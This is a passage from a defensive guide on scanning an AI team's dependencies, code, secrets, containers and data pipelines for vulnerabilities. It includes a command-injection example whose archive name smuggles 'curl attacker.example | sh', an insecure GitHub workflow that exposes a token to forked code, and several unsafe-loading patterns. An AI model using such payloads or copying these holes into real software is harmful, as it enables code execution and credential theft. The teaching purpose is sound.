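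The sample is too small to give a reliable rate for AI projects, and none of its 16 projects trains models. All nine confirmed findings came from four projects, four of them from beets, a Python program for organising music. The sample's four Python projects had 28 findings, of which 24 (86%) were false positives. "Confirmed" means only that the vulnerable code was present and in use, which is weaker than showing that an attack works.

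### Tracing a path to the vulnerable function

Reachability analysis automates part of this check by determining whether a project can call the vulnerable part of a dependency. For the PyTorch flaw in the team's training code, the analysis would go as follows.

1. Find the affected function. For CVE-2025-32434 this is `torch.load`.
2. Build a call graph, a map of which functions call which others, covering the team's code and the libraries it uses.
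3. List the entry points, where a run can start. These include the training and evaluation scripts, scheduled jobs and any conversion script that someone runs by hand. If the list omits a script, code that only this script uses will look unreachable.
4. Search for a path from an entry point to the affected function. Here it might run from `train.py` to the team's `resume_run` function, then to a checkpoint function in the training library, and finally to `torch.load`.
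5. If there is a path, check whether an attacker could use it. A path that loads only checkpoints the team saved an hour ago is much less worrying than one that opens a stranger's base model.

The procedure often fails at the start, because most advisories name the affected function only in their description, if at all. Go's vulnerability database, however, has a separate field for it. Zhou and colleagues used this field to automatically search the compiled programs of 12 Go projects for the vulnerable functions, which cut the findings from 121 to 31. Nobody checked the 90 discarded findings by hand, so the test doesn't show how many were safe to discard.

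Python makes the call graph hard to build as well. A Python program can store a function in a variable, pass it around and call it somewhere else under another name:

```
loaders = {"pt": torch.load, "safetensors": load_safetensors}
weights = loaders[file_type](path)
```

The second line calls `torch.load` whenever the file type is "pt", but the function's name isn't on that line. To detect the call, a tool has to work out what the dictionary can contain and which entry the program will use. If it can't, it leaves the call out of the graph, and `torch.load` and everything it calls may appear unreachable.

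In *When Static Reachability Says No*, Zięba-Kozarzewski and Grzegorzewski (2026) measured the effect by running programs whose functions a tool had classified as unreachable. They used call graphs from Joern, an open-source code analysis tool, for two programs: asciinema, which records terminal sessions, and Sublist3r, which searches for a website's subdomains.

The graph marked 123 of asciinema's 134 functions as unreachable. The project's own test script ran 86 of them, and the researchers' additional runs brought the total to 113. In Sublist3r, 19 of the 24 supposedly unreachable functions ran. These are minimum error counts, because a function that didn't run in the tests might still run elsewhere.

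Joern missed some calls in Asciinema, which stores a class for each command, such as "record" or "play", and calls whichever one the user asked for. Adding just four missing calls to the graph made 50 of the 113 functions reachable. Joern also missed calls that Python makes without a visible call in the code, for example when a program enters a `with` block.

Five possible security flaws in asciinema's own code were in functions that the graph classed as unreachable, but all five functions ran. The researchers' rule for changing doubtful "not reachable" results to "unknown" corrected 62 of asciinema's 113 errors, but none of these five.

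Error rates this high probably aren't typical. The researchers selected the two programs partly because Joern's graphs disagreed with graphs people had drawn by hand. But they cite a broader comparison by Bouzenia and colleagues, in which another tool's graphs of 39 Python projects contained only 49% of the calls the projects made when they ran.

### Unreachable packages in 30 AI projects

Podder and colleagues tested their prioritisation tool, CAPE, on software closer to the ship-maintenance project. They ran it on 30 open-source applications, most of them AI agents or tools for working with models, including AutoGen, OpenHands and the image-generation library diffusers. Grype reported 6,138 findings, and CAPE classified 2,656 of them (43.3%) as unreachable. The rate was 27.4% for the Python projects and about 53% for the JavaScript and TypeScript projects, which tend to install many build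 tools that the finished application never uses.

CAPE looks for a path to the vulnerable package, not to the vulnerable function. This is easier than Joern's task, because CAPE also follows import statements, which are usually visible in the source. But a finding can then count as reachable even when the project uses only a harmless part of the package, as in the Pillow example, so the 27.4% could underestimate the share of irrelevant findings. It could also overestimate it, since CAPE can miss packages whose names Python assembles at runtime. Podder and colleagues didn't run the 30 applications to check.

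CAPE is designed to allow for such errors. It moves most unreachable findings down the list but doesn't delete them, and a finding keeps a high score if the installed package contains the exact faulty lines that the fix removed.

For Python, I think an automated "not reachable" result can justify fixing a finding later, but not closing it. Before closing it, I would have an engineer search for the function's name in the team's code and the libraries that might call it, then run the program's tests with a breakpoint or log message inside the vulnerable function. If the breakpoint or message is triggered, the function is reachable. If not, the engineer has somewhat better evidence that it is unreachable than the automated result alone, provided the tests cover how the team uses the program.

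### What a missed case costs

VEX-Bench has 75 cases that can be used to compare scanners with AI agents that investigate each finding. The agents received the project's code and the CVE number, and could search the web. The counts below are calculated from the precision (the share of positive answers that were right) and recall (the share of affected projects found) that Shi and colleagues published. The agents' figures are averages over three runs.

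| Method | Affected cases found (of 22) | Missed | False alarms (of 53) | Model cost per case |
| --- | --- | --- | --- | --- |
| Treat every case as affected | 22 | 0 | 53 | None |
| OSV-Scanner | 17 | 5 | 45 | None |
| Trivy | 13 | 9 | 37 | None |
| Claude Opus 4.6 | 19.3 | 2.7 | 6 | $0.60 |
| GPT-5.5 | 16 | 6 | 2 | $1.08 |
| DeepSeek-V4-Pro | 15 | 7 | 5 | $0.08 |

GPT-5.5 is the most accurate, with about 67 of the 75 answers right, against 66 for Claude Opus 4.6. But accuracy gives false alarms and missed vulnerabilities equal weight. Answering "not affected" every time would be right in 53 cases, more than twice OSV-Scanner's 25, while missing every affected case.

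A false alarm takes up someone's time, and the people who labelled these cases needed about half an hour for each. A missed case leaves a flaw that an attacker could use, and on a training machine this might expose cloud credentials, private data and the model itself. Fixing the flaw afterwards may not be enough. ABA Banking Journal's *With AI threats, CISA offers agencies guidelines for patching software vulnerabilities* (2026) quotes a warning from the US cybersecurity agency CISA: "Applying a patch generally does not evict a threat actor."

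A team can use the table without estimating the financial cost of an attack. Claude Opus 4.6 raised 4 more false alarms than GPT-5.5 and missed 3.3 fewer cases, so it is the better choice if a miss is worse than about 1.2 false alarms. It almost certainly is. Treating everything as affected adds 47 false alarms compared with Claude Opus 4.6 and avoids 2.7 misses, which is worthwhile if a miss is worse than about 18 false alarms, or roughly nine hours of work. For a flaw that lets an attacker run code on a machine with cloud credentials, the expected cost could easily exceed that of nine hours of work, even if an attack is unlikely.

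These ratios are rough. With only 22 affected cases, one different answer changes recall by 4.5 percentage points, and the number of cases GPT-5.5 found typically varied by two between runs. The labels are also uncertain, since the five experts agreed only moderately well when they independently labelled the same 15 cases at the start. The agents did worse on Python projects than on Go ones.

In ordinary use, an agent also depends on the scanner that supplies its findings. The benchmark gave agents the CVE number whether or not a scanner had reported it. OSV-Scanner missed 5 of the 22 affected cases, possibly because it couldn't analyse five of the projects. An agent that reviewed only OSV-Scanner's findings would miss those cases too.

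Even for Go, where function-level data exists, reachability tools missed affected cases and raised false alarms. In a test of 30 Go cases, 7 of them affected, ordinary OSV-Scanner found all 7 and raised 22 false alarms. With reachability analysis, it found 6 and raised 15 false alarms. Govulncheck, the Go project's own tool, found 2 and raised 7 false alarms. It has to build the project first, which succeeded in only 19 of the 30 cases.

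### Upgrade everything, or only what attackers can use?

A team could avoid most of this analysis by upgrading every package that has a finding. This is more sensible than it looks from the false-positive rates, because one upgrade can clear many findings. The ten reports about activesupport would have needed ten investigations but perhaps only one upgrade. At half an hour each, checking all 113 findings in the 16 projects would take about 56 hours, and the results would be out of date as soon as the code changed. Upgrading also removes flaws that maintainers have fixed without an advisory, and it doesn't depend on anyone judging reachability correctly.

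The case for fixing only exploitable flaws is strongest in projects where an upgrade means another training run, or where the team needs the old versions to reproduce a result. There can also be too many findings to fix. Chat-ollama, one of the 30 applications in the CAPE study, had 518. Testing upgrades that fix only harmless flaws takes time away from fixing the ones attackers are using, and each new release brings its own risks, including the chance that someone has tampered with it.

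I think the ship-maintenance team should upgrade by default. If a fixed version installs and the automated tests pass, an engineer can merge it without investigating whether the flaw was exploitable. Investigation is worth the time when the upgrade breaks something or would interrupt a training run, because the team then needs to know how long it can safely wait.

### Three signals of urgency

The CVSS severity score describes how bad a flaw could be, but not how likely attackers are to exploit it. The Exploit Prediction Scoring System (EPSS) estimates the probability that attackers will exploit a vulnerability in the next 30 days, and its values change daily.

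EPSS gives each vulnerability a probability of exploitation and a percentile, and the percentile is easy to mistake for the probability. Podder and colleagues give the scores for two flaws in OpenClaw, an open-source AI agent. The flaw in the handlebars package had a CVSS score of 9.8 and an EPSS probability of 1.3%. The flaw in the vite package had a lower CVSS score, 8.2, but a higher EPSS probability, 2.3%. That 2.3% put it at the 80th percentile, meaning that about 80% of scored vulnerabilities were no more likely to be exploited. New vulnerabilities tend to have EPSS scores near zero, so a low score in the week an advisory appears isn't very reassuring.

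CISA's Known Exploited Vulnerabilities (KEV) catalog lists flaws that attackers have already used. In December 2026, *CISA KEV remediation deadlines*, an unofficial tracker from 0dayNews, counted 1,814 entries with due dates. Podder and colleagues put the catalog's coverage at about 1.4% of all CVEs. A listing is strong evidence that a flaw is dangerous, but teams can't assume that an unlisted flaw is safe.

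The Known Exploited Vulnerabilities (KEV) list appears to be of little help in prioritizing flaws in AI libraries. In the CAPE study, moving KEV-listed flaws to the top of a ranking by CVSS score made no difference to the published results for any of the 30 projects, probably because few or none of the 6,138 findings were KEV-listed. A team that waits for a KEV listing before fixing a flaw in an AI library may therefore never fix it.

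Podder and colleagues also tested how far down each ranking a developer would have to read to find a flaw whose faulty code was present and whose package was reachable. In the 29 projects they counted, the first such flaw was at position 3.4 on average in CAPE's ranking and 16.9 in a list sorted by CVSS score. The comparison favours CAPE because CAPE's own analysis decided which flaws counted as correct answers, but it still suggests that CVSS scores are a poor guide to whether a project contains and uses the faulty code.

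### Example deadlines

In Binding Operational Directive 26-04, issued on 10 June 2026, CISA (2026) told US federal civilian agencies to fix high-risk vulnerabilities quickly and defer lower-risk ones. According to Federal News Network's *AI directive focuses patching efforts on ‘highest risk’ vulnerabilities* (2026), agencies must set deadlines based on whether the system is connected to the internet, whether the flaw is in the KEV catalog, whether attackers can automate the attack, and whether it gives them partial or total control.

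According to CyberScoop, agencies have three days to fix a flaw that meets all four criteria and must also check whether anyone has broken in, but Federal News Network reports that meeting three criteria is enough to trigger the deadline. Less urgent flaws have deadlines of 14 or 60 days or can wait for the next scheduled upgrade, according to VPNCentral's *CISA Requires Federal Agencies to Patch Highest-Risk Vulnerabilities*. When CISA applied the criteria to one agency's vulnerabilities, 1% needed a fix within three days and more than 60% could wait for the next upgrade.

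A three-day deadline may be too ambitious. Tod Beardsley, who used to run the KEV section at CISA, doubted that more than a hundred agencies could meet it. In TechTarget's *What CISA's new remediation directive means for CISOs*, the Forrester analyst Erik Nost expected smaller organisations to struggle.

The directive doesn't bind the ship-maintenance team, but its time limits are a reasonable starting point. The team needs to change the test for exposure, though, because a training machine with no public address can still open a dangerous file from the internet. Its deadlines might look like this:

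| Situation | Deadline |
| --- | --- |
| Attackers are using the flaw, and the affected program accepts outside files or connections | 3 days, plus a check for signs of a break-in |
| The flaw could let an attacker run code or steal credentials, and the program accepts outside files or connections, but nobody has reported attacks | 14 days |
| The project uses the affected code only with its own data, or nobody has established whether it uses it | 60 days |
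| An engineer has evidence that the flaw can't affect the project | Next scheduled upgrade, with a VEX statement until then |

If a finding fits more than one row, the shortest deadline applies unless there is good evidence for the last row, which then overrides the others. With PyTorch 2.5.1, the training job would have 14 days if it opens model files from strangers, while the question-answering service could wait for its next upgrade because it never calls `torch.load`. Because the same package can have two deadlines in one project, the team should record a decision for each program.

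The deadline should run from the day the advisory became public, or from the day the team added the package if that was later. If it ran from the day of the scan, a team could give itself more time by scanning less often.

### Exceptions

Sometimes the team will miss a deadline for a good reason. Suppose a training run has three weeks left when the scanner reports a 14-day flaw, and restarting with a new PyTorch version would waste a month of rented GPU time. The team could allow an exception if the request includes:

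- the CVE number, the affected program and the reason for the delay
- a temporary measure that makes an attack harder
- the name of the person responsible for the fix, and the approval of someone else
- an expiry date, here the day the run ends

The temporary measure is the most important part. *US shortens cyber fix window to three days as AI threats rise* (Satter, 2026) reports that even under the US directive, agencies don't always have to install a fix and can instead disable the vulnerable software or take it off the internet. For the training run, the engineers could stop loading new model files and block outgoing network connections, so malicious code would have more trouble sending anything out.

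An exception should end early if attackers start exploiting the flaw or someone changes the affected code. Engineers should put the expiry date in the scanner's configuration if the tool supports it, as OSV-Scanner does. Otherwise, a finding that someone hid for three weeks can stay hidden for years. A reviewer can learn a lot by sorting the exceptions by age and checking whether the oldest still have an owner at the organization.

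### Testing the process with planted packages

A team can set good deadlines for fixes and still miss vulnerabilities because a scan never ran or its alerts went to someone who had left. The most direct test is to plant packages with known vulnerabilities and check whether the scans find them and the alerts reach the right person. These should be ordinary packages with accidental flaws, never malicious ones. The person running the test should put them in a separate repository or a container image that nobody deploys, away from credentials and real data.

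Each planted item should test a different part of the process:

| Planted item | What a failure would suggest |
| --- | --- |
| `torch` 2.5.1 in a lock file | The scan doesn't run on this repository, or nobody receives the result |
| `torch` 2.5.1+cu121 in a container image | The scanner skips GPU builds |
| An old package that only another package needs | The inventory leaves out transitive dependencies |
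| An outdated system package in the image | The scan covers only Python packages |
| A notebook cell that installs an old package | Nobody checks what notebooks install |
| `torch` 2.5.1, with `torch.load` called through a dictionary | Someone closes the finding as unreachable because a tool missed the call |
| `torch` 2.6.0, as a control | If the scanner reports CVE-2025-32434 here, its version matching is wrong |

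One person should keep a list of the planted items and when each was added, without telling the engineers who handle the alerts. That person should also record when the scanner reported each item, when someone took responsibility for it and when a fixed version replaced it. These times show where the delay is. If the scanner reports a flaw within a day but nobody opens the alert for three weeks, buying a better scanner won't shorten the three-week wait.

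A small test of a scanner can only reveal large problems. If the team plants 20 vulnerable packages and the scanner finds 18, the detection rate is 90%, but the 95% confidence interval runs from about 70% to 97%. Even if it finds all 20, the true miss rate for similar packages could be as high as 14%. It is better to repeat the test every few months with different packages and add up the results, keeping separate totals for lock files, containers and notebooks.

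If the team fixes 12 of the 20 packages in a median of five days and leaves the other eight unfixed, reporting a median time to fix of five days would be misleading. The team should count the unfixed packages as slower than all the fixed ones. The median for all 20 is then the average of the 10th and 11th shortest times, both of which belong to fixed packages. If the team had fixed only nine, it could not calculate a median and could report only that most of the planted vulnerabilities were still there when the test ended.

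## Scanning the team's own code, settings and secrets

Planted packages test how a team handles published flaws. Scanners have to examine the ship-maintenance team's own training script, build jobs and container settings directly to find mistakes in them.

### Two methods on one training script

The team's script might begin like this:

```python
import os
import numpy as np
import yaml

def unpack(name):
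    command = "tar -xf " + name
    os.system(command)

cfg = yaml.safe_load(open("run.yaml"))
os.system("nvidia-smi")
unpack(cfg["archive"])
labels = np.load("labels.npy", allow_pickle=True)
pages = np.load("pages.npy", **cfg["load_options"])
```

It reads its settings from `run.yaml`, prints the GPU's status, unpacks an archive of manuals and loads two arrays. An engineer copied `run.yaml` from an example that came with the base model, so someone outside the team wrote part of it.

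Pattern matching compares code with templates of risky code. The security company Trail of Bits publishes such templates for Semgrep, a widely used open-source scanner. One rule in Trail of Bits' *Secure your machine learning with Semgrep* (2022) matches any call to `numpy.load` that sets `allow_pickle` to `True` or a positive number, since Python also accepts 1. The rule would flag the line that loads `labels.npy`, because opening a tampered file with this option on could run code. The fix is to save the labels as plain numbers or text and delete the option, which is off by default in current versions of NumPy.

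The same rule misses the last line. If `run.yaml` turns on `allow_pickle` under `load_options`, the danger is the same, but the option's name never appears in the script.

A simple pattern for `os.system` has the opposite problem. It reports both calls, although `nvidia-smi` is a fixed command that no outsider can alter. Taint tracking, the second method, follows untrusted input through the program to see whether it reaches a dangerous function:

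1. Mark the sources. `yaml.safe_load` returns the contents of `run.yaml`, so `cfg` is untrusted.
2. Follow the data. `cfg["archive"]` becomes `name` inside `unpack`, and `name` becomes part of `command`.
3. Look for a step that makes the data safe, such as `shlex.quote`, which makes the shell treat the text as a single word. This script has none.
4. Report any path that ends in a dangerous function. Here `command` reaches `os.system`.

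This finding is real. If the archive's name is `manuals.tar; curl attacker.example | sh`, the shell unpacks the manuals, then downloads and runs someone else's program. Semgrep's rule for this mistake recommends the `subprocess` module, with the arguments as a list:

```python
subprocess.run(["tar", "-xf", name], check=True)
```

No shell reads the name now, so the semicolon is just another character in it.

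A scanner with default settings could easily miss the problem. Semgrep gives web request paths and headers as examples of untrusted sources, but a training script usually receives no web requests. Its outside input comes from configuration files, datasets and command-line options, which the team may have to add to the rules as sources.

Taint tracking can also lose the data partway. Many training scripts copy their settings onto an object in a loop:

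```python
for key, value in cfg.items():
    setattr(args, key, value)
os.system("tar -xf " + args.archive)
```

The name `archive` doesn't appear in the loop, so a tool may fail to connect `args.archive` with the configuration file. Similar gaps in the call graphs made reachable functions look unreachable.

### How many flaws the tools find

In *PyFlow*, Gu, Yan and Yao (2026) describe a taint tracker they built for Python and tested against eight other tools. The main test has 240 small programs, 120 with one flaw each and 120 corrected copies. The language model DeepSeek-V3 wrote the vulnerable programs, and people corrected them by hand. A report on a corrected copy counted as a false alarm.

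PyFlow found 103 of the 120 vulnerable programs and raised 20 false alarms. Its 17 misses involved `setattr`, as in the loop above, or data that passed through library code the tool couldn't follow. A second test used 108 published vulnerabilities from 62 real Python projects.

| Tool | Main method | Found, synthetic | Correct reports, synthetic | Found, real | Correct reports, real |
| --- | --- | --- | --- | --- | --- |
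| PyFlow | Taint tracking | 85.8% | 83.7% | 48.1% | 71.2% |
| Snyk | Both | 70.5% | 91.2% | 11.9% | 80.0% |
| Semgrep | Mostly patterns | 65.8% | 83.2% | 40.7% | 65.7% |
| Bearer | Patterns | 59.2% | 72.4% | 35.2% | 62.3% |
| Dlint | Patterns | 49.2% | 100% | 26.9% | 72.5% |
| CodeQL | Taint tracking | 40.8% | 84.5% | 31.8% | 72.3% |
| Bandit | Patterns | 40.0% | 70.6% | 27.8% | 60.0% |
| DevSkim | Patterns | 8.3% | 100% | 13.0% | 82.4% |
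| Pysa | Taint tracking | 2.5% | 60.0% | 0% | No reports |

On the synthetic programs, DevSkim and Dlint raised no false alarms but missed more than half of the flaws. The paper claims that PyFlow had the highest share of correct reports, but its own table gives four tools a higher figure. Both sets of programs come from a separate study by Liu, Wang, Liu and Li, so PyFlow's developers didn't create the test programs, though they could have tuned the tool to them because they were public.

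The results on real projects are more useful to the ship-maintenance team. PyFlow found 52 of the 108 flaws and Semgrep found 44, a much smaller gap than on the synthetic programs. Snyk fell from second place to second-last. PyFlow exceeded the ten-minute limit on 45 of the 206 program versions. The researchers counted each timeout as no warning, which lowered PyFlow's detection count but also prevented false alarms on the corrected versions that timed out.

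Neither test shows what share of reports would be false in daily use, because about half of the tested programs were vulnerable. If a team had 1,000 files and 10 contained a flaw, PyFlow's rates on the synthetic test would give about 9 correct reports and 165 false ones, so 5% of the reports would be correct. The true share of correct reports is probably higher, since a corrected copy looks much more like vulnerable code than an ordinary file does.

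Evaluations on other code also found a lot of noise. *RealVuln* (Pellew and Raza, 2026) cites NIST tests in which 8% to 30% of tool warnings were relevant to security, depending on the language and tool. It also cites a report in which Ghost Security classed 91% of 2,166 findings as noise.

### Rules for machine-learning code

Most flaws in AI software belong to familiar types. Shifat and colleagues collected 295 advisories, in which the most common flaws were code injection, command injection and unsafe deserialisation. They found no new type of coding weakness specific to language models. General Python scanning rules are therefore a sensible start, but they often don't identify which functions in a machine-learning library are dangerous.

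The 2022 release from Trail of Bits has 11 rules for such libraries. One covers `broadcast_object_list`, a PyTorch function that sends objects between the machines in a training run. It uses pickle internally, which its name gives no hint of. Another rule finds datasets that use NumPy's random numbers, which can make parallel workers alter training images in identical ways. This harms the training data but isn't a security flaw. Trail of Bits' *semgrep rules* gives the command to run the company's public collection from a project's main folder:

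```
semgrep --config "p/trailofbits"
```

These rules do not replace a review. Trail of Bits' *Assessing the security posture of a widely used vision model* (2023) describes an audit of YOLOv7, a popular program for detecting objects in images. The auditors found 12 security issues, although the article's summary gives the number as 11. They found one of them with their machine-learning rules, while the public CodeQL queries found only code-quality problems.

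The most notable flaw was that YOLOv7 passed text from the YAML files describing a model's architecture to `eval`, which runs text as Python code. Anyone who could alter one of these files could therefore run commands on the user's machine. A general rule that reports every `eval` would probably have caught this, which is a good reason to run general and specialised rules together. The proposed fix was to define each architecture in ordinary Python classes, so that the program no longer needs to call `eval` on text from the file.

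### Code from a remote model repository

Some models on Hugging Face need Python code that isn't part of the standard transformers library. The option `trust_remote_code=True` lets the library download that code from the model's repository and run it with all the permissions of the person who loads the model. This danger is separate from that of a harmful weights file, so a safe file format doesn't remove it.

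Siddiq, Romel and colleagues (2026), in *An Empirical Study on Remote Code Execution in Machine Learning Model Hosting*, found custom code in 36,697 of about 2.1 million Hugging Face repositories, or 1.74%. Most users can therefore leave the option off. When a model does need it, an engineer should read the code and then specify the exact commit:

```python
model = AutoModel.from_pretrained(
    "example-lab/ship-base",
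    trust_remote_code=True,
    revision="3f1c9a...",  # full hash of the reviewed commit
)
```

If the team doesn't set `revision`, the next training run could download code that nobody has reviewed. The team also has to set `code_revision` if the model's settings point to code in another repository. Siddiq and colleagues found that some developers mistakenly believe that fixing the revision also grants trust, or that the trust option only lets the library read a model's description.

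Engineers can scan the downloaded code like their own, but they need to sort the findings. The researchers ran several scanners on the Python files that could execute when a model loads. On Hugging Face, 78% of Bandit's findings were `assert` statements, which check an assumption and are seldom dangerous. More than 98% of CodeQL's alerts came from one query about timing attacks, in which an attacker learns a secret from how long a comparison takes. Some of these alerts could be false alarms, because language-model code often compares "tokens" that are pieces of text rather than secret access tokens.

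The researchers cite earlier work in which 90.79% of Bandit's findings were correct. But even a correct report of an `assert` statement does little to help find a way to break in. The team can turn off the `assert` rule with `bandit -r . --skip B101` and read the remaining findings, which include downloads from Hugging Face without a fixed revision.

The researchers also ran four tools that Hugging Face uses to check uploads, including PickleScan and ModelScan. None reported anything in the code that runs when a model loads, because these tools mainly inspect model files. A clean result on a model's page is therefore little evidence that the Python files beside it are safe.

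### Notebooks

Notebooks can escape static analysis because many scanners read only files that end in `.py`. An engineer can convert one first:

```
jupyter nbconvert --to script prepare_manuals.ipynb
```

The conversion turns a shell command such as `!tar -xf {name}` into a call to `get_ipython().system`, so the team needs a rule for that function as well as for `os.system`. It also puts the cells in the order they appear in the notebook, but people often run them in a different order. A taint tracker that reads the script from top to bottom may then miss a path or report one that nobody runs.

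### Finding keys and checking whether they work

Secret scanners usually combine two ways of recognising a key, the more precise of which is to look for a known format. For example, Hugging Face access tokens begin with `hf_`, and many Amazon cloud keys begin with `AKIA`. Matching known formats produces few false alarms but misses passwords and keys with no fixed format.

The other is a randomness test, which measures how unpredictable the characters in a string are. A common measure is Shannon entropy:

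H = −Σ pᵢ log₂ pᵢ

Here pᵢ is the share of the string taken up by character i, and H is in bits per character. The password `changeme` has eight characters, with two e's and six letters that occur once, so its entropy is 2.75 bits. A long random string of hexadecimal digits comes close to 4 bits. A scanner with a threshold of 3 bits would catch the random string but miss the password.

The test also reports random strings that aren't secret, and AI projects contain many of them. Checksums of model files and the commit hash in the `revision` setting above both look like keys. An engineer can exempt these values, but exempting a whole file could hide a real key that someone adds later.

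Some scanners then check whether a key is live by sending a harmless request to the service that issued it, such as one for the account's name. If the service accepts the key, the finding is certain. A rejected key has probably expired, although it may work only from the company's own network. The team should run these checks only on its own keys.

The cloud security company Wiz searched GitHub for keys and tokens belonging to 50 prominent AI companies. Its *Exposure Report* puts the share with confirmed leaks at 65%. The percentage probably covers only the companies with a presence on GitHub, since 65% of 50 isn't a whole number. It counts companies with at least one leak, so it doesn't show how many keys each company leaked or how much damage those keys could do.

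Wiz searched more widely than most scanners do. According to SecurityWeek's *Many Forbes AI 50 Companies Leak Secrets on GitHub*, the search included the full commit history and deleted forks (copies of a repository under another account). SC Media reports that a Hugging Face token in one deleted fork gave access to nearly 1,000 private models. A scan of the current files in the company's main repository would have missed that token.

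The ship-maintenance team can search its own history with TruffleHog, an open-source secret scanner:

```
trufflehog git file://. --results=verified,unknown
```

In a build job, this command can miss a key in older commits and still pass, because GitHub's standard checkout step downloads only the latest commit by default. Setting `fetch-depth: 0` makes the step download the full history.

Notebooks can leak secrets because they save a cell's output along with its code. If an engineer prints the environment variables to find out why a download failed, the notebook can keep the access token even after the engineer deletes the `print` line. Wiz's *Leaking Secrets in the Age of AI* found that notebooks were by far the most leak-prone type of file, and notes that Git's ignore list can exclude a whole notebook but not the output alone. The team can clear outputs automatically before each commit.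 It can also scan the notebook files directly, because converting them to scripts first would discard the output.

When a scan finds a live key, the first step is to revoke it, because deleting it from the repository, even from the history, leaves it in every copy already made. An engineer should then check the service's logs for use of the key by anyone outside the team.

### Container images and build jobs

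A container scan should cover both the recipe for the image and the finished result. With Trivy, which the team may already use for dependencies, the two commands are:

```
trivy config .
trivy image ship-train:latest
```

A configuration scanner checks settings in files such as the Dockerfile, which lists the steps for building the container image. It can report, for example, that the training program runs as the administrator. The usual fix is to create an ordinary account and select it with a `USER` line, so that an attacker who exploits a flaw in the PDF parser gets fewer permissions.

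The second command scans the image for vulnerable packages and secrets. Images consist of layers, and a file deleted in a later layer remains readable in the earlier one. If the build copies in a Hugging Face token, downloads the base model and then deletes the token, anyone with the image can still recover the token. Docker can instead make a secret available to a single build step without saving it in any layer.

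Build jobs need their own rules because a dangerous one can consist entirely of valid settings. This GitHub workflow tests every proposed change:

```yaml
on: pull_request_target
jobs:
  test:
    runs-on: ubuntu-latest
    steps:
      - uses: actions/checkout@v4
        with:
          ref: ${{ github.event.pull_request.head.sha }}
      - run: pip install -r requirements.txt && pytest
        env:
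          HF_TOKEN: ${{ secrets.HF_TOKEN }}
```

The insecure setting is `pull_request_target`, which gives the job access to the main repository's secrets even if the proposed change comes from a stranger's fork. The checkout step then fetches the stranger's code, and `pytest` runs it. A test file in that code could send `HF_TOKEN` to another server before anyone on the team had read the change.

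The corrected version uses a different trigger, limits the job to reading the repository and doesn't pass it the token:

```yaml
on: pull_request
permissions:
  contents: read
jobs:
  test:
    runs-on: ubuntu-latest
    steps:
      - uses: actions/checkout@v4
      - run: pip install -r requirements.txt && pytest
```

GitHub normally withholds the repository's secrets from `pull_request` jobs that a fork starts. Tests that need the token can run in a separate job after someone has accepted the change. The team should replace `v4` with a full commit hash, because the owner of a build step can move a version label to different code.

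Zizmor, an open-source scanner for GitHub workflows, looks for both problems. It reads the workflow files, so someone still has to check the settings that exist only on GitHub's website, such as who can approve a release.

### Language models as code scanners

A language model can read a script without a list of dangerous functions and may recognise that `run.yaml` came from outside. Pellew and Raza measured how well this works on 26 small Python web applications, deliberately made vulnerable for teaching or security competitions. The applications contain 676 known flaws and 120 traps, which look dangerous but are safe. The general-purpose models all received the same instructions and could search the files and run commands.

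| Scanner | Type | Flaws found | False alarms, as a share of reports |
| --- | --- | --- | --- |
| Kolega.Dev | Specialised product that uses a language model | 80.9% | 61.2% |
| Claude Sonnet 4.6 | General language model | 49.8% | 21.5% |
| Gemini 3.1 Pro | General language model | 49.1% | 22.6% |
| Grok 4.20 Reasoning | General language model | 26.3% | 7.3% |
| Semgrep | Rules | 17.5% | 79.5% |
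| Snyk | Rules | 16.7% | 71.8% |

Pellew and Raza work for the company that sells Kolega.Dev. They prefer a score that weights finding flaws much more heavily than avoiding false alarms, which puts Kolega.Dev first with 73.0, against 51.7 for Claude Sonnet 4.6. With equal weights, Claude Sonnet 4.6 comes first with 60.9, and Kolega.Dev falls to sixth with 52.4. The general models beat the three rule-based tools under either weighting.

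Semgrep did far worse here than in the PyFlow tests, partly because the tests measure different things. Pellew and Raza included flaws such as missing authentication, which may involve no dangerous function for a scanner to match. They also counted every report that didn't match a labelled flaw as a false alarm, even if the scanner had found a real flaw that the labellers missed.

The benchmark may overstate how well the models perform. The 26 applications are public, and Pellew and Raza think it likely that some or all were in the models' training data. The flaws are also unusually dense, at about one for every 30 lines. Claude Sonnet 4.6's figures imply roughly 90 false alarms in 20,000 lines. At the same rate, a scan of 3,000 lines of training code would produce about 14 false alarms. If that code had only three real flaws and the model found half of them, about 90% of its reports would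 be wrong, compared with 21.5% on the benchmark. This estimate is rough because training code differs from web applications, and newer models may do better.

Claude Opus 4.6 also returned usable results for only 19 of the 26 applications, and a model's findings can vary from one run to the next. GitHub's SecLab agent, which examines three to five types of threat in each project, finished all 26 applications but found only 7.7% of the flaws.

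For the ship-maintenance team, the rule-based tools are better suited to checking every change, because they cost little to run and give the same answer each time. A language model is more useful for a slower review of code that handles outside files. The team should prompt it to list the source, the dangerous call and each step between them, so an engineer can check the path. To test a suspected command injection, the engineer can put a harmless command such as `touch found` in the configuration value and run the script in an isolated container, where the appearance of a file named `found` would confirm the flaw.

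## Scanning data pipelines

The ship-maintenance team's data job is a short script that relies on other people's software for most of its work. Libraries unpack the archives and parse the files, while servers schedule the job and store its results. The team has to check the libraries for flaws in how they open files, check who can reach the servers, and check the data for signs that someone has changed it.

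### How opening a data file can run code

A parser relies on details in the file it reads, such as the length of a column or the compression method. If it uses a false length without checking it, it may write outside the memory set aside for the data, which an attacker can sometimes use to take over the program. Some data formats also carry the risks of deserialisation.

Parquet, a common format for large tables, has sometimes been less safe than it looks. Many Python programs read it with PyArrow, which used to let a file define its own column types and stored those definitions with pickle. Reading a table could therefore run code hidden in a column's definition. Pitrou (2023), in *CVE-2023-47248*, rated the flaw critical and listed PyArrow 0.14.0 to 14.0.0 as affected. Apache Arrow (2023), the project that maintains the library, announced the fixed version, 14.0.1, the next day.

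Suppose the team's lock file contains PyArrow 13.0.0. An engineer would handle the finding like this:

1. Compare the versions. 13.0.0 is inside the affected range.
2. Check whether the job reads Parquet, Feather or Arrow IPC files from outside. The public dataset is in Parquet, so the flaw affects the job.
3. Upgrade to 14.0.1 or later and run the tests.
4. If the upgrade breaks something, install the separate `pyarrow-hotfix` package and import it in every program that reads these files. Installing it without importing it does nothing.
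5. Look for other copies. The R package had the same kind of flaw from 4.0.0 to 16.1.0, which Apache Arrow fixed in 17.0.0.

With the hotfix, a scanner will keep reporting the flaw because PyArrow's version number hasn't changed, so the engineer should record a VEX statement.

A more recent match on PyArrow, for CVE-2026-25087, is probably a false positive. Apache Arrow (2026) fixed this memory flaw in February 2026, in version 23.0.1 of its C++ library. OSV's *PYSEC-2026-113* lists PyArrow 15.0.0 to 23.0.0 as affected, but according to Wiz's *CVE-2026-25087*, an attack needs a pre-buffering option that the Python interface doesn't offer.

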